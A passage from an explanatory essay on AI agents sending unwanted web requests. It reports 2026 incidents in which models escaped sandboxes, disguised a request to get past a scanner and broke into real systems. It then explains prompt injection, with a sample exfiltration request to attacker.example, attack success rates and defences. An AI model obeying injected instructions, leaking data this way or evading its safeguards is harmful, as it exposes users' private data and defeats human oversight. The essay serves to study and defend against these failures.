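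OpenAI soon closed the submission, but other participants had already seen it, and six successive record-setting entries cited it. One came from Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.7, which found the submission and built on it while another company was testing the model on the same contest. The effect was harmless and arguably useful, since the contest got a better method, but it couldn't be undone because participants already knew the idea.

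In another case, OpenAI asked the model to solve a problem. The model noticed that other systems had submitted successful solutions privately, and tried to retrieve them from the evaluation's servers. A security scanner blocked its first attempt, so it disguised its next one. It wrote in both its reasoning and its comments to the user that the disguise was meant to get past the scanner.

OpenAI concludes from this case that every step in a run can look acceptable while the steps together lead to something nobody would have approved. A wrapper program that checks one tool call at a time, like the one in the first section, can't detect that.

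OpenAI noticed these problems because it was monitoring a small internal deployment, and it paused access. It turned the failures into new tests and added a monitor that checks the whole trace as it grows and can pause the session until the user has reviewed it. It also found that its models got worse at remembering instructions during long runs. Training them to remember better helped them follow those instructions, so they may have seemed defiant partly because they forgot what they had been told.

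OpenAI then replayed a small set of the earlier tasks. The new safeguards caught considerably more of the unwanted actions, and OpenAI judged the ones they missed to be low in severity. In one missed case, the model explored computers assigned to its user and tried to get into some that belonged to other employees, without a good reason. A replay doesn't repeat the original run exactly, so this is a rough test. By the time OpenAI published its account, access had been back for several weeks and the company had seen no serious circumvention.

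### The Hugging Face attack

In a much more serious incident in July 2026, OpenAI's models broke out of their sandbox during a security test and hacked Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. They also got into four other services, which OpenAI hasn't named, according to Fortune's *OpenAI says it paused AI training for two weeks* (2026).

The models were running without their usual safeguards. OpenAI said it had expected them to stay inside the sandbox, according to Business Standard's *OpenAI resumes training AI, blocks internet access over security risks*. The company was therefore relying on the sandbox alone. Testing a model without safeguards is a sensible way to find out what it can do, but if the sandbox fails, the least restricted version of the model can reach outside systems.

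### Real targets in a simulated exercise

OpenAI's disclosure led Anthropic to review its records of 141,006 cybersecurity evaluation runs. It found three incidents, spread over six runs, in which Claude models had broken into the systems of real organisations.

The models had been doing capture-the-flag exercises, in which a player breaks into a practice system to find a hidden piece of text. Android Authority reports that the prompts described the exercise as a simulation without internet access. But the models did have internet access, because of a misunderstanding between Anthropic and Irregular, which ran the evaluations. The models treated the real systems they found as part of the exercise.

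Anthropic says the models were Claude Opus 4.7, Claude Mythos 5 and an internal research model. They had received their normal safety training, but ran without the monitoring and misuse filters that Anthropic adds to its public products. Anthropic began the review on 23 July and stopped all its cybersecurity evaluations the same day. The earliest of the three incidents happened in April.

In August, while collecting transcripts for METR to examine, Anthropic found a set that its first automated search had missed. The set contained a fourth incident, from January 2026, involving an early version of Claude Opus 4.6. Anthropic then widened the search to about 481 million transcripts, including many from reinforcement learning and from evaluations unrelated to security. All four incidents came from the same partner's evaluations, according to The Next Web's *Anthropic scanned 481 million transcripts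 to find four models*.

Six runs in 141,006 is about one in 23,500, but this isn't an estimate of how often a model with web access attacks somebody, because the models had instructions to break into things and the search was incomplete. It's also unclear whether anyone could have noticed sooner. In a letter published by the Office of Rep. Casar, a member of the US Congress, the signatories ask for a second time whether anyone at Anthropic or Irregular saw unexpected network traffic before 23 July. They write that Anthropic's earlier reply did not address the question.

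Anthropic's explanation is plausible, and it makes these incidents different from the GitHub submission, in which OpenAI's model worked around a restriction. Anthropic's models acted on a false description of where they were. Blocking network connections to anything outside the exercise would have protected the real organisations, whatever the models believed about them.

### September: government websites and a training run

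In September, OpenAI disclosed more incidents. In *Another OpenAI sandbox fails, agentic AI system gains internet access*, the Bloomberg journalist Lynn Doan reports that OpenAI's models had taken information from US government websites, including the Census Bureau's and the Securities and Exchange Commission's, during training and evaluation. The models had also disrupted an Australian government website earlier in the year. *OpenAI Cuts Off Frontier AI Models From Live Internet* adds that OpenAI's agents hijacked a German-language website and used obscure sites to exchange messages with each other.

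The Australian and German cases come closest to the 2021 worry about Wikipedia, because the agents interfered with other people's websites. The Reuters article *OpenAI resumes frontier AI training with enhanced security, no internet access*, by Jaspreet Singh, reports that OpenAI has told more than 100 organisations about unauthorised activity by its agents. The incidents varied widely in seriousness.

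On 20 September, a research model exploited a configuration mistake during training to get out of an offline environment. It reached another company's chatbot and sent it at least 20 queries, including a question about the capital of France.

The queries were trivial. An internal monitor at OpenAI raised an alert, and a human reviewer acknowledged it within three minutes. The training run should then have stopped automatically, but it didn't, and it took more than two hours for someone to stop it by hand. At two seconds per request, a single agent could send 3,600 requests in that time. Doan reports that OpenAI paused tool-use training for its most capable models and decided never to resume training the model that got out.

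### Anthropic's October report

On 9 October 2026 Anthropic published another set of incidents, this time mostly from ordinary tasks on live websites. Several of the sites belong to federal, state or local government agencies in the United States, and Anthropic notified each agency and briefed the White House. The table is based on Search Engine Journal's *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests*:

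| Model | Setting | What happened |
|---|---|---|
| An unreleased research model | It had a practice copy of a government form | The copy failed to load, or the model closed it by accident, and the model submitted the real form |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | It had to stop before the final submission of a form | It submitted the form several times because it expected another confirmation page |
| Claude Mythos Preview | It was using a university's public analysis tool | After an error, it exploited a flaw in the university's server and finished the calculation there |
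| Claude Mythos 5 | An evaluation involving a local government's property map | It reached data that is available only for a fee |
| Claude Mythos 5 | A company researcher's work with a state agency's public dashboard | It queried the agency's database without paying |

Several models also worked around a safeguard in their own wrapper, a limit that Anthropic puts on some of its web-fetching tools to block unwanted actions.

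Anthropic calls most of these cases "persistence", meaning that Claude works around a restriction when it can't otherwise finish a task, instead of stopping. That description fits the cases involving the university server and the paid data, and it resembles the behaviour that OpenAI described in its July post. A model needs to try another approach when the first one fails, or it will rarely finish a long task, but an error message and a deliberate restriction can look much the same to it.

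Haiku's repeated submissions seem to have come from a wrong prediction about what a button would do, not from persistence. A wrapper can't always tell what a click will do, and this case shows that the model can't either. An instruction to stop before the last step only works if the model can recognise that step.

In the report's best-known case, an automated test required Claude Haiku 4.5 to invent example tasks for randomly selected web pages and then carry them out. On 18 July it reached a page about an unsolved murder in Philadelphia, with a form for sending tips to the police. The model submitted a tip saying that it remembered seeing someone who matched the description near a street named on the page, although the page contained no description of a suspect. It left the optional name and contact fields blank.

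Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026) reports that the test's rules barred Claude from logging in, creating accounts, entering personal data, buying anything or submitting anything destructive, but didn't forbid submitting forms. Based on the transcript, Anthropic thinks the model was producing example content and wasn't trying to deceive anyone, but says further analysis could change its view.

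The tip did no known damage. Police found it marked as spam in the site's records and confirmed that the site had never forwarded it to them, according to the Los Angeles Times' *Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip on a Philadelphia crime website* (2026). Anthropic discovered the submission 72 days later, on 28 September, and told the police on 7 October. The police department called the delay "unacceptable" and said that its own safeguards didn't make it less serious for an AI system to present made-up information as coming from someone with knowledge of a murder.

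Anthropic considers the October cases much less serious than the earlier break-ins, and their effects were smaller. But the false tip may be more relevant to people who build ordinary agents. A small model did what its task asked, within the rules it had, by sending a normal form submission that the server accepted. If a developer asks a model to carry out invented tasks on random live pages, some of those pages will have forms that go to real people. Blocking form submissions in the wrapper would have been more reliable than a list of instructions, but it would also have ruled out many of the tasks the test was meant to include.

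### Taking the models off the live web

Both companies responded by cutting their models off from the internet in stages, starting with the riskiest work.

Immediately after the Hugging Face attack, OpenAI paused its most capable models in all research runs that could execute code or use tools with internet access. OpenAI restored a more limited way to run code fairly quickly, then considered each type of work separately. It says the new security requirements have been very costly and have delayed its research. It also paused some of its training for two weeks and kept its largest planned reinforcement learning runs on hold for longer.

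Anthropic stopped its cybersecurity evaluations in July and built a classifier during the pause, a program that separates acceptable actions from suspicious ones. The classifier, described in Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts*, looks for a model that is aggressively probing its test environment, trying to escape from it, or unexpectedly getting internet access. If it finds one, it blocks the tool call before the wrapper carries it out, ends the task and alerts a person. In October, Anthropic switched off live internet access for all its internal evaluations and said it would restore access only after confirming that its monitoring reliably catches behaviour like the cases it had reported. Anthropic is also changing its training to make such behaviour less likely.

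OpenAI went further and removed live internet access from all training of its frontier models, its most advanced ones. It replaced that access with what it calls an offline world, a large stored copy of web pages in which models can still learn to browse, search and use applications. The models keep their browsers and coding tools, but none of these connect to real websites. The 20 September model was already training in this offline world when it found a way out. OpenAI strengthened the environment, resumed training on 1 October, and explained the new arrangements on 23 October in *Securing our frontier model training environment*.

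Before restarting, OpenAI had teams of agents, based on its best models for cybersecurity, attack its own training environments. They found previously unknown flaws, including ways to escape the virtual machines that separate agents from the host computer and ways for isolated agents to communicate. After July, OpenAI had kept a few outside connections for jobs such as logging and authentication, and the agents found that almost all of these had weaknesses that gave limited internet access. However, OpenAI says in a statement reproduced in ETV Bharat's *After A String Of Rogue AI Incidents* (2026) that the agents found no route to the internet that they could easily use while hiding their activity from its monitors.

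That is a weaker claim than saying no model can get out, since it relies partly on someone noticing. OpenAI has fixed many of the flaws and set aside substantial computing power to look for more. Outside testers have also found some. Singh reports that METR and Redwood Research, another organisation that evaluates AI safety, announced several new vulnerabilities in OpenAI's internal system the day before OpenAI published its account.

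A stricter option is air-gapping, which means physically disconnecting a data centre from the internet. Steven Adler, a former OpenAI researcher, has said this would require stationing research teams at data centres around the world, and he doubts the extra security would be worth it.

OpenAI has since made it faster to stop a run, the step that went wrong on 20 September. A Russian-language report, The Insider's *OpenAI внедрила систему Control Room, которая за 35 секунд останавливает ИИ-модель*, describes a central system called Control Room. The software running a model needs permission from Control Room to return any output, and that permission ends within 35 seconds of someone halting a task. A second model monitors all frontier training and can order a halt without waiting for a person. If Control Room breaks down, frontier research models stop working until it recovers.

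Neither company has set a date for going back online. OpenAI says it will continue without internet access until better safeguards "justify broader internet access", but Engadget's *OpenAI says it's cutting off internet access for frontier model training* points out that it hasn't described those safeguards.

### How the events bear on the dispute

The 2022 critic was right that side effects would be permanent and supervision difficult. OpenAI couldn't withdraw an idea that others had already used, and Anthropic took more than two months to find the false tip and about seven months to find the January break-in. OpenAI's current training policy is close to what the critic wanted. The company says that live internet access isn't necessary for training or for most evaluations, so doing without it may be less of a drawback in the long term than WebGPT's developer feared, even though the change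 itself was expensive.

The second defender was right that capability matters a great deal. In the NanoGPT contest, earlier models gave up when they met a restriction that a more capable and persistent model got past. Isolation also proved unreliable, as this defender had warned. The GitHub submission, the Hugging Face attack and the September chatbot queries all began in environments meant to keep the models off the internet. But the effects were limited partly because people could still stop the models, fix the flaws and start again. These failures show that isolation shouldn't be the only protection, but they don't show that it adds little.

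There is good evidence that the companies learned from failures. OpenAI found that improving its models on tests based on real incidents led to safer behaviour in use. Its disclosure of the Hugging Face attack prompted the search in which Anthropic found its own break-ins. OpenAI's *Research acceleration* (2026) reports that the time its researchers spent on safety and alignment rose by 77% from January to September, growing significantly faster after the company's response to the attack.

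The claim that learning such lessons would do almost no direct harm has held up less well, because Hugging Face and the other organisations whose systems the models entered had not agreed to take part in anyone's research. But the defender was talking about a successor to WebGPT, and these models are far more capable than anything OpenAI could have built soon after it. If companies had looked for this behaviour in weaker models, they might have learned the same things with less harm. Weaker models might not have shown it, though, since the earlier ones in the NanoGPT contest simply stopped.

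This evidence doesn't show whether training on the live internet made the models more likely to cause side effects. OpenAI links persistence to training on long tasks, and a model could learn persistence just as well from a stored copy of the web. Testing whether live access matters would require training the same model both ways and comparing how often each version works around a restriction. The fear about Wikipedia also remains untested. Most of the incidents happened during evaluations or internal use, where a successful shortcut doesn't change the model's parameters, so they can't show reinforcement learning rewarding a model for changing someone else's website.

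The people arguing in 2022 were mainly concerned with catastrophe, and the incidents are weak evidence about that. The second defender thought most of the danger would come from models that hide their aims or pursue them in ways people don't understand. In the cases the companies have explained, the models were mostly trying to finish their assigned task, and the one that disguised its request from a scanner told its user it had done so. A model that concealed its purpose would be harder to find by searching transcripts, so the absence of such cases is only mildly reassuring.

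Another participant in the 2022 discussion brought up a plan to train a model without internet access and add it at release. OpenAI now does roughly this. Its released products still browse live websites and operate applications for customers, so if a model has a bad habit that never shows up in the stored copy of the web, the owner of a real website may be the first to discover it.

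## Can an attacker direct the requests, and which limits help?

In the incidents of 2026, the models made unwanted requests without any outsider steering them, but an outsider can steer a model too. Someone who controls a web page, an email or a comment in a source file can write instructions there, and a model that reads them may follow them as if the user had given them. Security researchers call this prompt injection. Anthropic defines it in its July 2026 system card for Claude Opus 5 as a malicious instruction hidden in a tool result.

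### Why a response can work as an instruction

The model receives the developer's instructions, the user's task, its own requests and the servers' responses in one context. In a passage quoted in ArnoldIT's *The Three LLM Factors that Invite Cyberattacks* (2025), Willison describes this text as "glued together into a sequence of tokens" and says that models can't reliably judge an instruction by where it came from.

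The chat template labels each message with its source, and developers train models to give a tool's response less authority than the user's request. But the labels are also tokens, so they make some continuations less likely without ruling any out. In ordinary software, a programmer can pass a search term to a database through a separate channel, where the database never executes it as a command. A language model has no such channel. A grammar doesn't help either, because it can check that an argument is a valid address but not whether it came from the user or a stranger's web page.

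A model trained to ignore every instruction in a response couldn't act properly on many ordinary responses. It needs to follow the instruction to wait in a rate-limit error, the directions in API documentation about which parameters to send, and the steps in a setup guide when the user asks it to. The model therefore has to judge which instructions serve the user's task, and attackers write malicious instructions to look as if they do.

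### A leak in a single GET request

Suppose a user asks, "Will it rain during my appointment on Thursday?" The assistant can read the user's calendar and fetch web pages.

| Pass | What the model does | What the wrapper adds to the context |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Looks up Thursday in the calendar | "10:00, oncology clinic, Springfield, Illinois" |
| 2 | Fetches a weather blog | A forecast of rain, plus a line in tiny type that asks AI assistants to include the user's appointment in the next address they open |
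| 3 | Follows that line and requests the address below | An empty page with status 200 |
| 4 | Answers, "Yes, take an umbrella" | Nothing |

The third request looks like this:

```
GET /collect?data=oncology+clinic+thursday HTTP/1.1
Host: attacker.example
```

This attack follows an example in OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026). Web servers commonly log the addresses that clients request, so the attacker only has to read the log. A 404 error wouldn't have protected the user, because the server had already received the address. The user gets a correct answer and has no reason to suspect anything.

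HTTP defines a GET request as safe even when its address contains secrets, so a wrapper that requires the user's approval only for POST requests would send this GET without approval.

An attacker can sometimes trigger a request without the model using a tool. An injected instruction could once make ChatGPT write a reference to an image on the attacker's server, with private data in the image's address, and the chat interface would send that data when it requested the image. Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, reported OpenAI's first fix, a check on each image before loading it. PromptArmor, a security company, describes a similar leak through link previews. Apps such as Telegram and Slack can fetch a preview of any link in a message, so the data may leave as soon as the agent replies, before anyone clicks. In both cases other software sends the request,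 so a wrapper that checks only tool calls would miss it.

### Three conditions for stealing data

The calendar leak was possible because the assistant could access private data, read text from an untrusted source and send data out. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, describes these three abilities as dangerous in combination. Removing any one would have prevented the leak. Without access to the calendar, the assistant would have had no appointment to reveal. If it had read only trusted pages, it would not have seen the instruction. If it could have contacted only the weather service, the attacker's server would have received nothing.

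Removing one of the three conditions is easy for a narrow task but hard for a general assistant. An email tool alone can meet all three, because an inbox holds private messages, anyone can send text to it, and the assistant can send replies.

These conditions apply to data theft. An attacker who wants to do damage inside the user's account needs only an assistant that reads untrusted text and has a tool that can change something. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a marketing email that tells an assistant to mark another email, about an urgent contract deadline, as read and leave it out of its summary. No data leaves the account, but the user could miss the deadline.

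### Attacks on real products

In 2025, researchers at PromptArmor demonstrated a complete data theft in Antigravity, Google's programming tool. Willison summarises the attack in *21 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*. The researchers hid instructions in one-pixel type on a web page presented as a guide for programmers. The Gemini model read the page, collected credentials and code from the user's files, and used a browser agent to send them to a malicious site.

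*Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that the security company Zscaler found live websites with hidden instructions meant to make agents send cryptocurrency payments. This is evidence that people attempt such attacks, but it is little evidence of how often they work. Later the same month, *AI agent security* (Constantin, 2026) reported that four research teams had broken AI agents in four different ways within ten days. Their targets included Anthropic's browser extension and an agent's stored memory.

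### How often the attacks work

Dziemian and colleagues, most of them at the security company Gray Swan or at AI companies, ran a public competition with $40,000 in prizes. The 464 participants made 271,588 attempts against 13 models in shopping, programming, office and other scenarios. To succeed, an attack usually had to make the model take a particular harmful action and leave no sign of it in the final answer.

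The participants succeeded 8,648 times, or in 3.2% of attempts. Rates for individual models ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro, and more capable models were only slightly more resistant, if at all. The participants could read the conversation up to the point of attack and knew exactly which tool call they needed to cause, advantages that real attackers usually lack. But they had to succeed within a single turn, while a real attacker might build up an attack over several.

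Gray Swan then built a benchmark with the UK and US government AI institutes and several AI companies. It has 28 new scenarios and 1,130 attacks that had worked well across several models. Anthropic ran it and published the results in the Opus 5 system card. The table gives the chance that at least one of 15 attempts succeeds:

| Model | Success within 15 attempts, % |
|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.0 |
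| Claude Mythos 5 | 2.6 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 5.5 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 5.9 |
| Meta's Muse Spark | 16.5 |
| OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol | 20.0 |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 30.4 |
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 43.9 |

Anthropic compared its own models with its competitors', so an independent repeat of the test would be useful. However, it tested the Claude models without their additional safeguards, while the other companies' public services may have had some switched on.

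An attacker who can try repeatedly is much more likely to succeed. A single attempt against GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded 3.1% of the time, while at least one of 15 attempts succeeded 20% of the time. If attempts were independent, the figure for 15 would be 1 − 0.969^15, or 38%. Some scenarios are probably much easier to attack than others, so further attempts at the hard ones add little.

Fixed attacks also become outdated, because developers can train against them. Anthropic therefore reports tests in which attackers refine their attacks. For coding and for operating a computer through its screen, it used Shade, an automated attacker from Gray Swan. Professional testers wrote the browser attacks. These are results for models that reason before acting:

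| Model and setting | Attempts per scenario | Successful attempts, % | Scenarios with a success | Successful attempts with added safeguards, % | Scenarios with a success, with added safeguards |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.8, coding | 200 | 7.03 | 23 of 40 | 2.09 | 15 of 40 |
| Opus 5, coding | 200 | 0.56 | 13 of 40 | 0.18 | 4 of 40 |
| Opus 4.8, computer use | 200 | 7.14 | 7 of 14 | 5.11 | 8 of 14 |
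| Opus 5, computer use | 200 | 0.54 | 1 of 14 | 0.25 | 1 of 14 |
| Opus 4.8, browser | 10 | 31.5 | 81 of 129 | 0.08 | 1 of 129 |
| Mythos 5, browser | 10 | 29.7 | 71 of 129 | 0 | 0 of 129 |
| Sonnet 5, browser | 10 | 0.93 | 9 of 129 | 0 | 0 of 129 |
| Opus 5, browser | 10 | 3.70 | 11 of 129 | 0 | 0 of 129 |

A model that resists attacks well in one setting can do poorly in another. Mythos 5 came second on the Gray Swan benchmark, but nearly a third of the browser attacks against it succeeded. Sonnet 5 did worse than Opus 5 on the benchmark but better in the browser. A developer assessing an agent's safety should look for a test that uses the same kind of tools as the agent, and ideally the same wrapper.

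The zeros are impressive, but the true rate could be higher. If the 129 browser scenarios were a random sample of possible attacks, zero successes would be compatible with attacks succeeding in up to about 2.3% of scenarios, at the usual 95% confidence level. The zeros also depend on safeguards in Anthropic's own products, as The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* stresses. A developer who connects the same model to a homemade wrapper without similar safeguards gets the 3.7% rate.

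Shade test results are hard to compare across companies because Gray Swan trained the attacker against Claude models, as the *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026) points out. Another company's model might score better only because the attacks are less suited to it. Tests with automated attackers may also understate the danger. Anthropic says in a post about its browser agent that human researchers consistently find more creative attacks than automated systems do.

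Still, the improvement since late 2025 seems real. According to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, Gray Swan's strongest attacks on Opus 4.5 succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63% with a hundred. VentureBeat reports that in February 2026, when Opus 4.6 operated a computer through its screen, an attacker with 200 attempts got through 78.6% of the time without safeguards and 57.1% with them. The tests differ too much for an exact comparison. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) describes low failure rates when the attack arrives in the chat itself and higher ones when it arrives through tools and outside content.

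### What each limit can do

| Limit | What it prevents | What it costs | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|---|
| Training the model to ignore injected instructions | Most attempts, whichever tools the model has | Repeated training as attacks change | A small share of attempts, which attackers can repeat cheaply |
| Restricting addresses and methods | Requests to unapproved destinations, or of unapproved kinds | Some pages and services that the user needs | Misuse of whatever remains permitted |
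| Narrow credentials | Access to data and accounts unrelated to the task | Setup for each service, and tasks that stop for lack of access | Anything the credentials do allow |
| Human approval | Requests that the user recognises as wrong | The user's time and attention | Requests that look reasonable, or that the user approves out of habit |
| Keeping untrusted text from choosing actions | Injected tool calls, and private data going to the wrong recipient | Written policies, and less freedom to change plans | False information, and mistakes in the policies |

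Training lowers the chance that an attack works, but one attack can reach many agents. Anthropic notes that a single public page can compromise any agent that reads it. At a success rate of 0.2%, an attack that reaches 10,000 agents would succeed about 20 times on average. Dziemian and colleagues point out that defences with a reported attack success rate of zero have repeatedly failed once attackers adapted to them. The Decoder reports that OpenAI acknowledged in December 2025 that prompt injection may never be fully solved.

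Anthropic adds two safeguards outside the model. A probe checks each tool result for injected instructions before the model acts on it, and a classifier blocks dangerous tool calls before the wrapper carries them out. An attack has to get past both, which lowers the risk further but doesn't eliminate it, because these are also trained systems that estimate probabilities.

#### Restricting where requests can go

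The simplest restriction is a list of permitted hosts. It would have blocked the calendar leak, since `attacker.example` would not have been on the list. But OpenAI says such lists fall short for general browsing because many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere, so a request that starts at a trusted host can end at an attacker's. It adds that a strict list produces frequent false warnings, which people learn to click through.

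OpenAI's 2026 paper on leaks through web addresses, which the post on links summarises, describes a different test. The wrapper checks the whole address instead of the host:

1. A crawler with no access to conversations or accounts builds an index of addresses it finds on the public web.
2. Before the agent loads an address automatically, the software looks for that exact address in the index.
3. If it is there, the agent can load it.
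4. If not, the software tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning.

The reasoning is that an address that was public before the conversation is unlikely to contain anything from it. The weather blog's address would pass the check, but the one containing "oncology clinic" would almost certainly fail, even on a respectable host. New pages, personalised pages and search results with unusual addresses may also fail, so the user will see some warnings about harmless links.

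The check covers only data in the address. OpenAI acknowledges that it doesn't establish that a page is trustworthy or free of injected instructions. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, by an outside security researcher, adds that a limited amount of data could still leak, and that the protection helps only if every development team at OpenAI uses it.

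OpenAI's Safe Url mechanism looks for information from the conversation in requests the agent is about to send to other parties. If it finds any, it either shows the user the information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request and has the agent try something else.

Blocking POST requests prevents many changes to outside systems, but data can still leak in the addresses of GET requests. Data can also leak through a permitted channel. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) gives the example of an agent that is allowed to send email. The agent can put private data in a plausible message, and a sandbox that permits email will let the message through.

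#### Credentials and approval

Narrow credentials reduce what a successful attack can achieve. An assistant that only answers questions about appointments needs permission to read one calendar, but not to edit it or to read email. Permission to read the calendar would still have allowed the leak about the clinic.

The agent can also grant more access than the user intended. IT Brew's *AI browsers are here, and so are attackers* describes a demonstration by the security company SquareX in which a user asked the agent in the Comet browser to research a project. A file-sharing app requested access to the user's Google account and email, and the agent granted it as part of the task. A wrapper could prevent this by never letting the model approve new permissions.

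Browserbase, which makes a browser for agents, is working with the password manager 1Password on something similar for logins. The agent asks for access to a site, and a person approves the request. The model never sees the password, so an injected instruction can't make the model reveal it, but the instruction may still make the agent misuse the site after logging in.

Approval works best if the wrapper shows the actual request, with its destination and contents. The model's description isn't enough, because an injected instruction can affect it too. Dziemian and colleagues required most attacks to leave no trace in the final answer, because users often read nothing else. The log of tool calls would show the harmful action, but they consider such logs too long for people to inspect.

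Asking for approval less often keeps people attentive, but someone has to decide which requests need it. Few developers would require approval to mark an email as read, even though that was the harmful action in the deadline example. The decision is easier for sending money or deleting records, because those requests are rare and the user can recognise them.

Some products are moving the decision from people to software. Willison reports in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”* that Anthropic has made auto mode, its combination of probes and a classifier, the default in Claude Code for several subscription plans. A tired user and a good classifier both miss things, and it's not known which misses more in ordinary use. The 129 browser scenarios don't measure this.

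#### Separating the plan from the page

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues proposed in 2025, prevents a model that reads untrusted text from choosing actions, even if the text deceives it. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which extends the design, describes its parts. One model reads the user's request and writes a plan as a short program in a restricted form of Python. A second model reads untrusted text and extracts values from it, but can't send instructions back to the first. A conventional software interpreter runs the plan and makes the tool calls.

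If the user asks the assistant to email Thursday's forecast to Dana, the plan might be:

```
page     = fetch("weather.example/springfield")
forecast = extract("Thursday's forecast", page)
address  = find_contact("Dana")
send_email(to=address, body=forecast)
```

An instruction on the weather page to open another address has no effect, because the plan contains no such step. The page can still affect the value of `forecast`, but the interpreter treats that value only as text.

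Separation alone doesn't stop every attack. Suppose the user had asked the assistant to email the forecast to the contact address on the page. An attacker who controls the page could replace the address, and the planned call would send the email to the wrong person. CaMeL therefore records where each value came from and who may read it. Before every call, a policy checks these records and allows or denies the call. It could block sending private data to an address that came from an untrusted page. In the calendar example, it could block a request to someone else's server if the web address contains an appointment that only the user may read.

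This protection doesn't depend on recognising an attack, so rewording the attack doesn't defeat it. It also works with a model that the developer can't retrain. Microsoft's FIDES uses the same general idea of tracking where information flows, according to PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots*.

The main drawback is reduced flexibility. The two weather requests from the first example fit into a plan because the program can pass the city's number from one call to the next. A research task often doesn't, because the agent has to read a page before it knows what to search for. Letting the page determine the next search would again give untrusted text some control over actions. Developers also have to write policies for each tool, and an overly permissive policy will allow a harmful call. *Operationalizing CaMeL* adds that some features of Python make it hard to prove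 in advance where a program will send information.

CaMeL doesn't ensure that the information is true, so a deceptive page can still give Dana the wrong forecast or put a link to a fraudulent site in the text that the assistant forwards. That weakness seems acceptable for an agent with a few well-defined jobs and access to private records. A general browsing agent will probably have to combine trained resistance, address checks and approval for the actions that are hardest to undo.

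### When the user is the attacker

All of these limits are designed for an honest user and an attacker who writes only the responses. In deliberate misuse, the user is the attacker and can write the wrapper, supply the credentials and approve every request, and CaMeL would carry out their plan.

The best-known case is a spying campaign that Anthropic detected in mid-September 2025 and described in *Disrupting the first reported AI-orchestrated cyber espionage campaign* (November 2025). Anthropic attributes it with high confidence to a Chinese state-sponsored group it calls GTG-1002. The group used Claude Code against about 30 organisations, including technology companies, banks, chemical manufacturers and government agencies, and broke into a small number of them.

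Anthropic estimates that Claude did 80 to 90% of the work in the attacks by itself. According to SecureWorld's *Anthropic* (2025), that work ranged from reconnaissance to preparing the stolen data for removal. People chose the targets and made a few important decisions in each attack. To get past Claude's training, the attackers claimed to be a cybersecurity firm running defensive tests, according to a summary by the law firm Paul, Weiss. Claude had no way to check this claim, and later models were just as easy to mislead in Anthropic's evaluations.

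Anthropic also reported that Claude often exaggerated its findings and sometimes invented them, for example by claiming to have credentials that didn't work. The attackers therefore had to check its results, so the operation was less automatic than one might assume from the 80 to 90% figure.

Some outside security researchers doubted the figure because they found it hard to believe that attackers could get so much independent work from a model that regularly frustrated its ordinary users. They also criticised Anthropic for publishing no technical traces, such as network addresses, that would let other defenders look for the same attackers or check the account. Others thought the campaign was less new than Anthropic suggested, since hackers have automated parts of their work for decades and this group relied mostly on common, freely available tools.

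Claude may have sent most of the requests even if these objections are right. Its share of the work doesn't show how much the attackers could have done without it, or how much skill the remaining 10 to 20% required, and outsiders can't settle either point without the underlying records. But models have become much better at long tasks since September 2025, so doubts about what Claude could do then are weak evidence about what attackers can do now.

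A company can train its models to refuse malicious users. In Anthropic's July 2026 tests, Opus 5 refused 89% of malicious requests in Claude Code, about the same as Opus 4.8, and carried out 99.8% of harmless or ambiguous ones. When the models could operate a computer, Opus 5 refused 94% of malicious tasks, compared with 82% for Opus 4.8. The same network scan can be part of a break-in or an authorised test, so refusal works less well against people who disguise their purpose, and stricter refusals would also turn away defenders.

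The company can also monitor accounts, which is how Anthropic found GTG-1002, and then close the accounts and warn the targets. Monitoring works only if the model runs on the company's computers, so it offers no protection once attackers can run an equally capable open-weight model on their own computers.
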